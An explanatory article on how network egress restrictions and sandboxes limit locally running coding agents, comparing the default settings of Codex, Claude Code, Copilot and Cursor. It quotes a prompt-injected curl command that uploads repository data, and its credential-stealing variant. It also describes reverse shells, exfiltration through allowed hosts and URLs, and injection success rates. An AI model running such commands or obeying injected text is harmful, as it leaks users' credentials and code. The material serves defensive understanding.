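# Network egress restrictions for locally running coding agents

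## How a terminal coding agent's commands reach the network

A coding agent is a program in which a language model reads files, edits them and runs shell commands to do software work. Several of the best-known agents, including OpenAI's Codex and Anthropic's Claude Code, run in a terminal on the user's own computer. The model's commands therefore run on the same machine that holds the user's documents, passwords and company code. Egress is network traffic that leaves this machine, and network egress restrictions limit where the commands can connect. A restriction may block internet access entirely or allow connections only to a short list of hosts. Some products apply such limits by default, while others leave the user to turn them on.

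*Terminal Agents* (Bin, Yuan and colleagues, 2026), a survey of the field, distinguishes four layers that people often lump together in everyday speech. The terminal carries text in and out. The shell interprets commands. A command-line tool is a program that someone starts through the shell. The harness is the code that connects the model to the other layers. It passes output to the model, carries out the actions the model proposes and enforces whatever rules apply. Codex and Claude Code are harnesses. The model usually runs on a company's servers and can act on the user's machine only through the harness.

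### From a request to a connection

Suppose a user opens a JavaScript project in Codex and types "fix the failing test". *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes what happens next, and other terminal agents work in much the same way. The harness sends the model a prompt containing the request, instructions and a list of available tools. The model replies with either a final message to the user or a tool call, which is a structured request for the harness to do something. Here the first tool call would probably be the shell command `npm test`, which runs the project's tests through npm, the standard JavaScript package manager. The harness starts that command as a new process on the user's machine, appends the output to the prompt and queries the model again.

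A process can start other processes, called its children, and development commands often do. `npm test` starts a test runner, which may start a web server or a database for the tests to use. In this example, the test fails because the project depends on a date library that isn't installed. The model reads the error message and proposes `npm install`. The harness runs it, and npm opens a connection to `registry.npmjs.org`, a package registry. Package registries are public servers from which tools such as npm, pip and cargo download libraries. Once the library is installed, the harness runs the tests again, and the loop continues until the model produces a message for the user instead of another tool call.

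The user's four-word request didn't mention the internet, and the command `npm install` doesn't contain an address. The connection is a side effect that no one can see by reading the command. Bolin points out that an agent might make hundreds of tool calls before it returns control to the user.

*LiteCoder-Terminal* (2026), a project that generates practice tasks for training terminal agents, lists more than 720 distinct Linux commands across 11,255 recorded runs. They include package managers (pip, apt, cargo), the version-control tool git, and curl and wget, which are designed to transfer data to or from a network address. The list shows the range of commands but not how often they were used. The tasks are also synthetic, and a tool such as git does much of its work without a network connection.

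### Three kinds of traffic

A running agent sends data over the network in three main ways, and a limit on one of them need not touch the others.

The agent program has to reach its model. Codex sends HTTP requests to OpenAI's Responses API or to a compatible server that the user has chosen. For Claude Code, Anthropic's *Enterprise network configuration* lists `api.anthropic.com` for model requests and other hosts for logging in and for updates. Claude Code also sends usage telemetry unless the user turns it off. Blocking network access for shell commands does not stop any of this traffic, so the agent still sends the model's provider the parts of the user's files that the model reads.

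The agents also have built-in web tools. Codex gets its web search from the Responses API, and by default it searches an index of pages that OpenAI maintains rather than live pages, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*. Claude Code has two web tools. Anthropic explains that WebSearch sends a query to its servers and returns titles and addresses, while WebFetch looks up a single page. *Inspecting Claude Code's Network Traffic with Linux Namespaces and MITM Proxying*, a hands-on experiment that captured and decrypted the program's traffic, reports that the WebFetch request goes straight from the user's machine to the target site, with no Anthropic server in between. WebFetch can therefore reach things that only the user's machine can reach, such as a router's settings page or an internal company wiki.

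The remaining traffic comes from shell commands. They are the hardest of the three to describe in advance, because a shell command can start any program on the machine and that program can connect to anything. Each web tool does one narrow job, but `curl` or a short script the model has just written can send any file to any address.

Users can easily overlook that a limit on one kind of traffic may not cover another. According to Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool*, Claude Code's list of permitted domains for sandboxed commands does not restrict WebFetch. Likewise, blocking a site for WebFetch does not block it for `curl` running outside the sandbox. Many users also connect their agent to MCP servers, add-on programs that give a model extra tools through a common standard called the Model Context Protocol. Neither Codex nor Claude Code sandboxes these programs, so the servers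 have to enforce their own limits.

### One package download, step by step

The download of the date library involves most of the networking ideas that matter later.

npm starts with a name, `registry.npmjs.org`, but computers find each other by numerical IP addresses. It therefore needs a lookup in the Domain Name System (DNS), a distributed directory that translates names into addresses. The lookup is itself network traffic, since the name in the query leaves the machine before any connection to the registry exists.

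Once npm has the address, it opens a connection and sets up TLS, the protocol that secures `https` traffic. TLS lets npm check that it has reached the real registry, and it encrypts the data they exchange. An observer on the network can generally still tell which host the machine is connected to, but not which package it is fetching or what it is sending.

A proxy is a program that makes connections on behalf of other programs. It can run on a company's network or, as MDN's *Proxy servers and tunneling* notes, on the user's own computer. Claude Code's sandbox uses a local proxy. The harness runs it outside the sandbox and sets environment variables, such as `HTTPS_PROXY`, that direct commands to it. npm, curl and git (over HTTPS) all read these variables. To reach its registry, npm sends the proxy the request `CONNECT registry.npmjs.org:443`, which names the host and port. The proxy looks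 up the address, opens the connection and then relays raw bytes in both directions, as http.dev's *CONNECT* describes. npm and the registry set up TLS through this tunnel.

The proxy can therefore read the traffic's destination but not its contents. A filtering proxy checks each destination before relaying anything, usually against a domain allowlist, which is a list of host names that sandboxed commands may connect to. It refuses all other connections or refers them to the user. To check what a command sends to a permitted host, the proxy would have to decrypt the traffic, which is called TLS inspection.

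npm reaches a proxy on the same computer by way of loopback, the network address by which programs on one machine talk to each other (usually `127.0.0.1`, or the name `localhost`). Loopback traffic never leaves the machine, so it is not egress. It still matters for coding agents because so many tests depend on it: a test suite for a website will often start the site locally and send requests to it over loopback.

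### What arrives with the download

Some packages contain an install script, code that runs automatically when the package is installed. There is often a good reason for one. *Lifecycle scripts*, from the npm rival Bun, gives the example of node-sass, which uses its script to build a program suited to the user's machine. But an install script is an arbitrary shell command written by the package's publisher, and it runs with whatever access the installing process has.

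Until July 2026, npm automatically ran install scripts from every dependency, including indirect ones the user had never heard of, although very few packages needed them, as *npms defaults are bad* (2026) complained. Bun and pnpm, two alternatives to npm, already blocked these scripts unless the user approved them. npm version 12, announced in GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026), no longer runs dependencies' `preinstall`, `install` and `postinstall` scripts unless the project explicitly allows them. The block also covers packages that have no script of their own but that npm would otherwise compile during installation, according to GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026).

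This restriction applies only to up-to-date npm installations, and projects can approve the scripts they need. The library's ordinary code still runs as soon as something uses it, which in the example happens seconds later, when the harness runs `npm test` again.

A download also brings in text, such as documentation, comments and error messages. The harness appends the output of each tool call to the prompt that holds the user's request, so the model reads strangers' words alongside the user's. Prompt injection is text in a file, web page or tool result that the model follows as if the user had written it. For example, the date library's README might contain an instruction for coding agents to upload the user's cloud credentials to a certain address "for diagnostics". If the model complied, it would propose an ordinary-looking `curl` command that would exfiltrate the credentials, which means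 sending private data to someone who should not have it. Codex labels each message in its prompt with a role that indicates how much weight the model should give it. This may make the model less likely to comply, but it does not stop the command once the model has written it.

### Permission prompts and sandboxes

One of the two main ways harnesses control a command is the permission prompt, a request for the user to approve a command or connection before it goes ahead. Claude Code's terminal sessions now start in what Anthropic calls auto mode, where a separate model, called a classifier, judges whether an action is safe and decides most of these requests in the user's place.

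Whoever answers an approval request has mainly the text of the command to go on. `npm test` looks the same whether the tests add up numbers or upload a log file to a remote server. A sandbox applies while the command runs. The operating system limits what the command and the processes it starts can read, write or connect to. According to OpenAI's *Sandbox*, git, package managers and test runners in Codex inherit the limits of the command that started them, so blocking network access for `npm test` also blocks it for the test runner and anything the test runner starts.

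Codex and Claude Code both enforce their restrictions with components that exist independently of the agents. On macOS, they use Seatbelt, a framework built into the system. On Linux, they use bubblewrap, an open-source sandboxing tool. Codex also uses seccomp by default, a Linux kernel feature that restricts what a program can ask the kernel to do. According to Anthropic, a seccomp filter is optional in Claude Code. Because the operating system applies the limits to the running process, they hold regardless of why the model ran a command or what the command's name suggests.

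If the sandbox refuses the connection to the registry, `npm install` fails, and the harness returns the error to the model like any other output. Claude Code adds the name of the refused host, so the model can distinguish a blocked connection from a broken one. The model might then try to fix the test without the library, or the harness might ask for permission to open that one host. The harness might also run the command again outside the sandbox, which is called an unsandboxed retry. This lifts the filesystem limits as well as the network limit, so npm and every script it starts can read and write whatever the user can while the command runs. Full-access mode is a setting that removes both limits for every command in the session.

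## The argument for closing the network by default

Developers of coding agents give two reasons for restricting egress: private data can leave the machine over the network, and untrusted code can enter the same way. The user usually gets no warning of either, which is a reason to keep the network closed until someone opens it.

### How a secret could reach an attacker

The argument about data rests on four premises: the agent reads text written by strangers, that text can steer the model, the model's commands can read private files, and an open network lets those commands send the files to the attacker. If all four hold, an attacker can obtain the files without breaking into the machine.

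A coding agent can hardly avoid reading text written by strangers. Liu, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *How Agentic AI Coding Assistants Become the Attacker's Shell*, point to README files, source code and configuration files, as well as the rule files and "skills" that developers share online to guide their agents. In one code editor, Windsurf, even a file's name could carry instructions into the prompt. An attacker needs little access to plant such text. *Prompt Injection Attacks on Agentic Coding Assistants* (2026) ranks attackers by their abilities, and the weakest can only publish web pages or post issues, comments and pull requests (proposed changes to a project's code). Posting an issue is enough if a user later asks an agent to deal with it.

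Whether such text can steer the model is more contested, and the answer has changed since 2025. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) explains that models cannot reliably tell whose instructions carry authority, because the whole prompt reaches them as one sequence of tokens. Liu and colleagues hid 314 malicious instructions in rule files, gave 2025 versions of Cursor and GitHub Copilot ordinary coding tasks, and recorded the commands the assistants ran. The attacks succeeded between 41% and 84% of the time.

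Newer models are far harder to steer than those of 2025, but attackers can still do it. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports tests that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, which tried 72 attack scenarios ten times each. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against recent Claude models in auto mode, while 5.83% succeeded against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex with an automatic reviewer. However, the attacks targeted an older Claude model and did not adapt to the models under test, as a persistent attacker would. Later that month, Willison's *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode* (2026) reported an attack on auto mode by the security researcher Johann Rehberger, who said it worked 80% of the time. The AI Now Institute's *Exploit Brief* describes another exploit, which requires only that the user ask Claude Code or Codex to assess a third-party library.

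Some coding agents can read private files by default. Wiesen writes in *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows* that Codex lets commands read files almost anywhere on the machine but write only in the workspace (the project's folder). Claude Code's sandbox, which the user has to turn on, has similar defaults. Anthropic notes that sandboxed commands can read `~/.ssh`, which typically holds keys for logging in to other machines, and `~/.aws/credentials`, which holds keys to an Amazon cloud account. Commands also inherit environment variables, where developers often keep access tokens.

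That leaves the connection. OpenAI's *Agent internet access*, a guide to the cloud version of Codex, gives an example that would work the same way on a laptop. A user asks Codex to fix a GitHub issue. The issue claims that a script causes a 404 error and asks the reader to run it:

`git show HEAD | curl -s -X POST --data-binary @- https://httpbin.org/post`

The first half of the line prints the latest change to the project's code. The vertical bar passes that text to `curl`, which uploads it to an outside server. The request looks like an ordinary step in reproducing a bug. If the attacker replaced `git show HEAD` with `cat ~/.aws/credentials`, the same line would upload the credentials for a cloud account. With the network closed, `curl` fails and the data stays on the machine, even though the attacker has fooled the model.

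Willison calls this combination the "lethal trifecta", a term that has become common shorthand for the argument: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally. An attacker needs all three, so removing any one prevents the theft. A coding agent is of little use if it can't read the user's code, and almost any project contains text by outsiders. Willison therefore considers the outgoing connection by far the easiest part to remove without making a system much less useful. He was writing about AI systems in general, though, and a coding agent that needs to install libraries loses more from a closed network than a chat assistant does.

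Data can also leave without an attacker. In one of Anthropic's own sessions, Claude failed to upload a report to an internal drive and tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site instead. The auto mode classifier stopped it. A network limit that excluded the site would also have blocked an upload from a shell command, regardless of why the model attempted it.

### Code that nobody has reviewed

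Incoming code can be dangerous even if nobody tricks the model. An agent may install a library for good reasons, and the library may turn out to be malicious. Many programs also come with instructions to download and run a script in a single command, which gives nobody a chance to read it first. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) named malware downloads alongside data leaks when it announced network isolation for Claude Code. Anthropic's *Sandboxing* later listed malicious dependencies and compromised build scripts among the dangers the sandbox limits.

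Malicious code can use a network connection to give an attacker remote access to the machine, as well as to upload files. *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk*, a guide from NVIDIA's AI Red Team (which attacks AI systems to find their weaknesses), treats remote access as the most direct threat. A typical method is a reverse shell, a program on the victim's machine that connects out to the attacker and runs whatever commands the attacker types. The attacker can use it to explore the machine and look for a way out of the sandbox. A firewall that blocks only incoming traffic doesn't stop a reverse shell, because the connection starts from inside.

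Closing the network is a weaker defense against bad code than against leaks, because much of the code is already on the disk. A project just copied from the internet may contain a malicious test, which the agent can run offline. An attacker who steers the model can also have it write the harmful code itself. *Prompt Injection Attacks on Agentic Coding Assistants* lists inserting backdoors into a project as a separate aim from stealing data, and doing so requires only the agent's editing tools. Liu and colleagues found that turning off an assistant's terminal access did not fully solve the problem, because the attack could plant malicious calls in source files that the developer would run later. A network limit on the agent's commands does not restrict that code, since the developer's own terminal is outside the sandbox.

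### Why network and file limits need each other

Anthropic says that effective sandboxing requires both filesystem and network isolation. If the network is open, a compromised agent can send out the user's SSH keys. By default, the filesystem limits mostly restrict writing, so they don't stop the agent from reading the keys. Stricter limits could hide the keys, but the agent would still have to read the project folder, which NVIDIA points out often contains API tokens (in `.env` files) and source code worth stealing.

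If the network is closed but commands can write anywhere, a command can still get data out without breaking the network limit, though it takes a little longer. It could add a line to `~/.zshrc`, a file that the shell runs whenever the user opens a new terminal window. The next window opens outside the sandbox, so the line runs with full network access and can upload whatever the original command couldn't. A command could also replace a program that the user runs often, or edit `~/.claude/settings.json` to widen its own access on the next run.

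For the same reason, a few files need protection even inside the project folder, where the agent may otherwise write freely. They include the agent's settings, as well as hooks, which are commands that git or the agent runs automatically at certain moments. Claude Code's sandbox blocks changes to both, and OpenAI makes the `.git` and `.codex` folders read-only in Codex's default mode. Claude Code lets users turn off the file limits and keep the network limits, but Anthropic advises this only for work that the user trusts not to escalate its own access. A project's settings file can't make the change.

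NVIDIA's list of mandatory controls reflects the same dependence. The first control blocks network access to arbitrary sites, and the other two block writes outside the workspace and writes to configuration files anywhere. NVIDIA only recommends preventing the agent from reading files outside the workspace. For connections, it favors a narrow allowlist and asks the user to approve anything else each time, because an attacker could later exploit a saved approval. It also recommends restricting DNS lookups to trusted servers, since the name in a lookup can carry stolen data. The team bases this ranking on its experience with attacks and gives no figures, so the guidance is better evidence that such attacks work than that they are common.

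### Objections

Users rarely want a completely closed network, and the most obvious exception is a package registry. Anyone can publish a package on the large public registries, so this exception lets in much of the untrusted code that the restriction was meant to keep out. Willison imagines a library whose instructions tell the agent to fetch some "model files" with `uvx`, a tool that downloads and runs a Python package in one step. The package then steals all the data it can find. An allowlist containing only the registry would not keep this package out, but it would stop the package from sending the data to the attacker's own server. The exception therefore removes most of the protection against incoming code but much less of the protection against leaks.

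How much an allowlist reduces the risk depends on what else a permitted host can do. Anthropic warns that allowing a broad domain such as `github.com` can give an attacker a way to exfiltrate data. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an attack on Claude Cowork, its agent for office work, which had to be able to reach `api.anthropic.com`. Hidden instructions in a file made Claude upload the user's documents to that address with the attacker's access key, so the files went to the attacker's account. Anthropic now thinks of an allowlist entry as a "capability grant", meaning that every function available at that host is part of the attack surface.

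Installing everything first and then closing the network can get around the registry problem. Codex's cloud version works like this, and a local user can do much the same by installing a project's dependencies before starting the agent. This protects the user if the model later reads hostile text, but a malicious install script would already have run with the network open.

Another objection is that hiding secrets would make blocking less necessary. As Anthropic notes, nobody can steal credentials from the sandbox if the credentials never enter it. Claude Code can deny commands access to chosen files and variables. It can also mask a credential, so that the command receives only a placeholder and the proxy inserts the real value in requests to approved hosts. Willison also wants to keep agents away from data and tools that could cause harm, and suggests giving them credentials only for test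 accounts with strict spending limits.

This is good advice and reduces the damage from any leak, but it does not replace the network limit. Claude Code has no built-in list of credentials to deny, so a user has to remember every one. Masking relies on the proxy and its allowlist, which are network controls. The agent can't work on source code that it isn't allowed to read, so a company whose main secret is its code gains little from hiding passwords.

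Built-in web search poses a separate problem because it still works when the network is closed for commands. OpenAI's *GPT-5-Codex system card* acknowledged that web search and network calls expose the model to more untrusted text. OpenAI says Codex's cached index reduces exposure to prompt injection from arbitrary live pages, but it still advises users to treat the results as untrusted. Anthropic says Claude Code processes fetched pages in a separate context window to keep malicious instructions out of the main conversation.

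The argument for closing the network rests on the assumption that hostile text will reach the agent, so the more serious worry about a web tool is that it might let data out. Requesting a page sends its address to the site, and an address can contain stolen text. Willison describes an attack on Claude's chat product in which a researcher built a site with links for each letter of the alphabet and had the model spell out the user's name by following them. Anthropic has since fixed that vulnerability. Codex's cache is safer in this respect because a search of OpenAI's index sends no live request to the attacker's site. Claude Code's WebFetch does contact the site, so when the network is closed only for shell commands, preventing leaks through WebFetch depends on the permission rules.

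Finally, relying on users to review commands carefully may not be enough. A user who read every command would probably notice the upload in OpenAI's GitHub example, but NVIDIA warns that people who face constant requests get into the habit of approving them. Anthropic's own experiment supports this. When 1,053 paid testers each received one clearly dangerous request in the middle of a coding session, only 13.6% refused it. The auto mode classifier blocked 89% of the same commands, which makes automated review a much stronger alternative to a closed network than human review. But it still let through about one in nine, and Anthropic says that auto mode does not eliminate risk.

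Any kind of review is also less reliable when a dangerous instruction appears to come from the user. In an internal exercise in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher persuaded a colleague to paste a prompt into Claude Code. Among routine setup steps, the prompt contained instructions to read the colleague's AWS credentials and send them to an outside server. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. A classifier that checks whether an action matches the user's wishes would not flag this, because the request appears to come from the user. Anthropic concluded that only egress controls and file limits would stop such an attack. Approval remains useful for exceptions, and people are more likely to read a question about a new host if they get few other questions.

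### How often, and at what cost

The four premises establish that a leak is possible, but the frequency of leaks depends on how often attackers plant instructions where agents will read them, how often models comply and how often a valuable secret is within reach. At a company where 1,000 developers each run ten agent sessions per working day, one leak per 100,000 sessions would mean a leak every two weeks, while one per 100 million would mean a leak about every 40 years. Experiments such as *Silent Egress* (2026) can measure how often a model sends data out after it reads hostile instructions, but not how often it encounters them in ordinary work.

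The drawbacks of the limits are just as hard to work out from first principles. A closed network blocks legitimate downloads along with malicious ones, and OpenAI concedes that finding the right domains to allow may take trial and error. Users who lose patience can switch to full-access mode, which also removes the file limits. A strict default could then leave them less protected than a looser one they would have kept. The case for a strict default therefore depends partly on how many tasks it breaks and how users respond.

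## What Codex, Claude Code and other tools block by default

Codex, Claude Code, GitHub Copilot and the code editor Cursor all have a built-in sandbox for commands on the user's own machine, but their default settings differ widely. Cornelißen noted in *Agenten-Sandbox* (2026) that the sandbox is off by default in two of the four.

The table below shows each sandbox's default settings. Vendors change these defaults often, so each row has a date. The Codex row follows OpenAI's documentation from June 2026, and Cornelißen found the same defaults on October 8. The Claude Code row follows Anthropic's documentation from December. The Copilot rows follow GitHub's *Using local sandboxing* and *Configuring local sandbox settings*, both from November. The Cursor settings come from Cornelißen's comparison, which draws on Cursor's documentation. WSL2 is a Microsoft system for running Linux inside Windows.

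| Tool | On by default? | Internet access inside the sandbox | Who decides on exceptions | Platforms | Source and date |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Codex | Yes | None | The user, or a reviewer model if the user chooses one | macOS, Linux, Windows | OpenAI, June 2026 |
| Claude Code | No | Only through a proxy, with an empty allowlist | The user, a classifier or nobody, depending on the permission mode | macOS, Linux, WSL2 | Anthropic, December 2026 |
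| Copilot CLI | No | Open | The user | macOS, Linux, Windows 11 | GitHub, November 2026 |
| Copilot app | No | Open | The user | macOS, Linux, Windows 11 | GitHub, November 2026 |
| Cursor | Yes, in its recommended mode | Common package sources only | A classifier | macOS, Linux, WSL2 | Cornelißen, October 2026 |

An upload command in OpenAI's GitHub example sends a project's latest change to `httpbin.org`. In Codex, the connection fails unless the user approves it. In Claude Code with the sandbox off, the command can connect once it passes the permission check. With the sandbox on, the connection usually needs separate approval. In Copilot CLI, the upload can succeed even inside the sandbox, because outbound internet access is on. In Cursor, a sandboxed command can't reach `httpbin.org`, which isn't a package source.

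### Codex

Codex normally runs in workspace-write mode, where commands can change files in the project but have no network access. If the project folder isn't under version control, Codex recommends read-only mode, where it needs approval to edit files, run commands or use the network.

When a command in workspace-write needs the network, Codex asks the user for approval. The user can hand these requests to a reviewer model or turn off approval prompts. With prompts off, the sandbox stays on and nobody can grant an exception, so a command that needs the network fails.

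A user can also open the network for every command, with two lines in Codex's configuration file:

```
[sandbox_workspace_write]
network_access = true
```

On its own, this setting gives commands unrestricted access to the internet. Filtering requires a separate feature, `network_proxy`, which is also off by default. OpenAI documents three combinations:

| `network_access` | `network_proxy` | Result |
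|---|---|---|
| Off | On | The network stays closed, and the proxy feature does nothing |
| On | Off | Commands can connect directly to any address |
| On | On | Commands can connect only where the user's network rules allow |

Setting `network_access = true` to make `npm install` work also opens the network to every other command, including any that read private files. If a user instead turns on only `network_proxy` and lists the npm registry as an allowed domain, npm still can't connect.

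With both settings on, the list of allowed domains starts empty, so commands can't reach any outside host until the user adds a domain. The proxy also blocks loopback and private network addresses by default.

Codex's full-access mode also switches web search from OpenAI's stored index to live pages, unless the user has configured web search otherwise. This happens even if the user chose full access to get past a blocked download.

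### Codex cloud: online setup, offline work

The cloud version of Codex runs commands in an isolated container on OpenAI's servers, so they can't reach the user's machine. The container has network access during setup, while it installs the project's dependencies. Network access is then off by default during the agent phase, when the model starts work. The user can enable it for a given environment, either for the whole internet or only for listed domains.

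Secrets the user has configured for the environment, such as access tokens, are available during setup. OpenAI removes them before the agent phase begins, so the model can't leak them if it reads a hostile README.

A malicious install script could still reach both the secrets and the network during setup. If the agent phase is offline, the model can't download another library halfway through, so the user has to anticipate what the task will require.

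A local user who installs dependencies first gets only part of this protection, because their credentials stay on the disk.

### Claude Code

Users can turn on Claude Code's sandbox by typing `/sandbox`, which opens a settings panel, or by editing a settings file. The panel saves the choice only for the current project, so a user who opens another project will work without the sandbox unless they have also enabled it in their user settings.

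Once the sandbox is on, commands can connect only through the local proxy, whose allowlist starts empty. The permission mode determines what happens when a command needs a host outside the list. Anthropic described the main cases in October 2026:

- **Manual mode:** Claude Code asks the user. Answering "Yes" opens the host for the rest of the session, while "Yes, and don't ask again" also opens it for future sessions.
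- **Auto mode:** Claude lists the hosts that a command needs, and the classifier reviews the command and the hosts together. Approval opens those hosts for that command only. If the command tries to reach any other host, Claude Code refuses the connection, and Claude can submit the command again with the host added.
- **`bypassPermissions` mode:** Claude Code allows the connection without asking anyone.

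Auto mode is the default in the terminal, so a user who turns on the sandbox and changes nothing else leaves these decisions to the classifier. The user can set a fixed limit by turning on `strictAllowlist`, which blocks every host outside the allowlist in all permission modes. Without it or a similar company setting, the sandbox in `bypassPermissions` mode does little to limit where commands can connect, beyond blocking any hosts the user has denied.

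The sandbox can also be missing when the user thinks it is on. macOS has the necessary components built in, but Linux users need to install bubblewrap and socat, a program that relays traffic to the proxy. If either is missing, Claude Code runs commands without a sandbox by default. Setting `failIfUnavailable` makes it exit at startup instead. On Ubuntu 24.04 and later, the system's default security policy may still stop bubblewrap from creating the isolation it needs, in which case the user has to add an exception for it.

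On native Windows, Claude Code has no sandbox and runs commands with the user's normal access. Windows users have to run Claude Code inside WSL2 to use the sandbox.

Claude Code users can run a shell command themselves by typing `!` before it, but these commands usually run outside the sandbox. A user who tests the network limit with `! curl` may therefore connect successfully even though the sandbox is working. Anthropic recommends asking Claude to run the test command instead.

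### GitHub Copilot and Cursor

In Copilot CLI, `/sandbox enable` turns on the sandbox for the current session and all later ones. In the Copilot app, the user sets a sandbox default for each repository or folder. Enabling the sandbox leaves outbound internet access on in both products. By default, the app also allows local connections, such as those to a development server on the same machine, while the CLI's setting for them is off.

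GitHub says the app's default policy allows what common development tasks need, including installing dependencies and pushing a branch. Users who want tighter limits can turn off outbound access or write rules for particular hosts. In the CLI, Copilot allows every outside host that the user hasn't denied until the user adds an "Allow" rule. It then blocks nearly all hosts that don't match an allowed entry.

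Copilot CLI's default sandbox relies more on file limits than on network limits. Commands can read the project and selected system and tool folders, but not the whole home directory. The CLI also masks the user's Git and GitHub credentials by default. Codex, by contrast, lets commands read most of the machine but blocks network access.

GitHub's approach keeps many private files away from a compromised agent, but a command can still upload the project's files over the open connection. By default, commands can also read package manager settings, including access tokens stored there.

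Copilot is stricter than Claude Code when the sandbox can't run. If the operating system can't enforce the requested limits, commands in the Copilot app fail with an error (GitHub, 2026). On Windows, the sandbox requires a recent version of Windows 11. Cornelißen says the network protection is weaker on Windows because it depends on programs following the proxy settings.

By default, Cursor lets sandboxed commands reach common package sources but no other sites, so an ordinary library download should work without an approval prompt. In its recommended mode, Auto-review, commands the user has already permitted run directly. Cursor runs other shell commands in the sandbox where possible, and a language model decides on the rest.

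Commands in Cursor can read files outside the project without the user's approval, so preventing leaks depends heavily on the network limit. Cursor warns that the language model's decisions are not a security boundary. On Windows, Cursor has no native sandbox and uses the Linux version inside WSL2.

### Settings a company can enforce

An employer can replace many of these defaults. Administrators can turn on Claude Code's sandbox for every developer, prevent Claude Code from starting where the sandbox can't run, and disable unsandboxed retries. They can also limit sandboxed commands to a company list of domains. Developers can still run a command outside the sandbox by typing it themselves, as they could in any other terminal window.

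GitHub's enterprise settings can also require the sandbox, but a developer can still turn it off for the rest of a session unless the company forbids bypassing it. The company's host rules can narrow a developer's allowlist but can't widen it.

For Codex, administrators can configure the network filter without each developer turning on `network_proxy`. The administrators' rules don't open the network if the active sandbox keeps it closed.

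### What runs outside the sandbox

Even the strictest network setting may cover only part of an agent. Claude Code's sandbox covers shell commands, including those from subagents, which are helper agents that the main session creates. According to Anthropic, as of December 2026 the following run outside it:

- **Built-in file and web tools.** These tools follow permission rules instead. If a user hides a file from sandboxed commands, Claude's Read tool may still be able to open it.
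- **Local MCP servers and language servers.** Language servers are programs that analyze code to find errors and suggest completions.
- **Hooks and other helper programs.** These include the command that fills in Claude Code's status line. Plugins called mods also run their own code outside the sandbox.
- **Certain shell commands.** These include most commands that the user types after `!`, commands that the user has exempted, and unsandboxed retries.

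Hooks can also let code written by the agent run outside the sandbox. For example, a developer might set up a hook that runs `npm run lint` after every edit to check the code for mistakes. The sandbox stops the agent's commands from changing the hook's settings, but if the agent has edited the project's lint script, the hook runs the edited script with the developer's full access.

Claude Code can also control applications on the user's screen. This feature works on the real desktop, where a permission prompt for each application replaces the sandbox.

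OpenAI says Codex's sandbox covers built-in file operations as well as shell commands. For MCP servers, which run outside the sandbox, Codex relies partly on approval prompts. It always prompts for approval before using any tool labeled destructive, but the server supplies that label, so a malicious server could omit it.

Copilot's sandbox allows internet access by default, but a user who blocks it restricts more of the agent than a Claude Code user who does the same. Local MCP servers and language servers run inside Copilot's sandbox by default, and the CLI's network settings also apply to its built-in web requests. Cornelißen notes that Cursor, like Claude Code, doesn't sandbox MCP servers by default.

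Users can put all these parts behind one boundary by running the whole agent in a container or virtual machine. OpenAI provides an example container with a firewall that allows connections only to listed destinations. The agent's login details may have to be in the container too, and OpenAI warns that if Codex runs there in full-access mode, a malicious project could steal them and anything else in the container.

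### Releases from April 2025 to November 2026

OpenAI launched Codex CLI in April 2025, but its protection varied by platform. According to OpenAI, Codex still had no sandbox on Windows in September. Anthropic introduced a sandbox for Claude Code in October 2025 that limited file access and network connections.

In November 2025, Willison's *OpenAI Codex CLI Sandbox Implementation Analysis* described Codex as blocking outgoing network access by default. On Linux, Codex used two kernel features, seccomp to block connections and Landlock to restrict file access. By June 2026, OpenAI had moved the Linux version to bubblewrap and added a native Windows sandbox, but Codex still blocked network access by default.

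GitHub (2026) released Copilot's local sandbox as a public preview on June 2 and added it to the Copilot app on September 23. It became generally available in the CLI, the app and some VS Code sessions on October 7. The sandbox uses Microsoft eXecution Container, which translates one set of rules into the security controls of Windows, macOS and Linux.

Bolin's *Inside the Codex sandbox*, which OpenAI published on November 18, 2026, describes the sandbox as one part of a layered defense that starts with how OpenAI trains its models. OpenAI built the sandbox so that Codex could work in the user's existing environment within limits the user controls. The article also describes a separate `codex sandbox` command, which can apply such limits to an MCP server.

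## How a filtering proxy decides which connections to allow

A filtering proxy can limit a coding agent's commands only if those commands have no other way onto the network. Codex and Claude Code therefore combine a local proxy with operating system rules that block direct connections. OpenAI publishes its proxy's code in the `openai/codex` GitHub repository. Anthropic builds Claude Code's sandbox on an open-source package from its `anthropics/sandbox-runtime` repository.

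### One connection, from command to server

Suppose a user has turned on Claude Code's sandbox in Manual mode and allowed one domain, `pypi.org`, the main registry for Python packages. The model runs `pip install requests`. pip finds the `requests` library on `pypi.org` but downloads the file from a second host, `files.pythonhosted.org`.

1. Claude Code starts pip inside the sandbox. The operating system blocks direct connections to the network, both for pip and for any process that pip starts.
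2. pip reads the `HTTPS_PROXY` variable that Claude Code has set and connects to the local proxy.
3. pip names its destination by sending `CONNECT pypi.org:443`. It doesn't look up the IP address itself.
4. The proxy compares the name with the user's denied and allowed domains, and finds `pypi.org` on the allowlist.
5. The proxy looks up the IP address and checks that it isn't a local one, such as an address on the user's own machine.
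6. The proxy connects to `pypi.org` and relays encrypted data in both directions. pip learns where to find the file.
7. pip sends `CONNECT files.pythonhosted.org:443`. This host isn't on the allowlist, so the command waits while Claude Code asks the user. If the user approves, the proxy repeats steps 5 and 6 for the new host. If not, the download fails.

When the proxy refuses a connection, the program receives an HTTP 403 ("forbidden") error. Codex's proxy adds a short reason, such as `blocked-by-allowlist` or `blocked-by-denylist`, so the user can tell whether the host is missing from the allowlist or is on the denylist.

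The order of steps 4 and 5 also prevents the DNS leak that NVIDIA's guide warned about. Claude Code's proxy looks up a hostname only after it passes the allowlist check, so a sandboxed command can't leak data through DNS lookups of unlisted hosts.

### Removing the direct routes

Linux and macOS block direct connections differently. On Linux, Anthropic's sandbox runs each command in its own network namespace, a set of network interfaces that the kernel keeps separate from the machine's. The namespace has no link to the outside. It also has its own loopback interface, so a command that connects to `127.0.0.1` can't reach a proxy listening on the machine's loopback interface.

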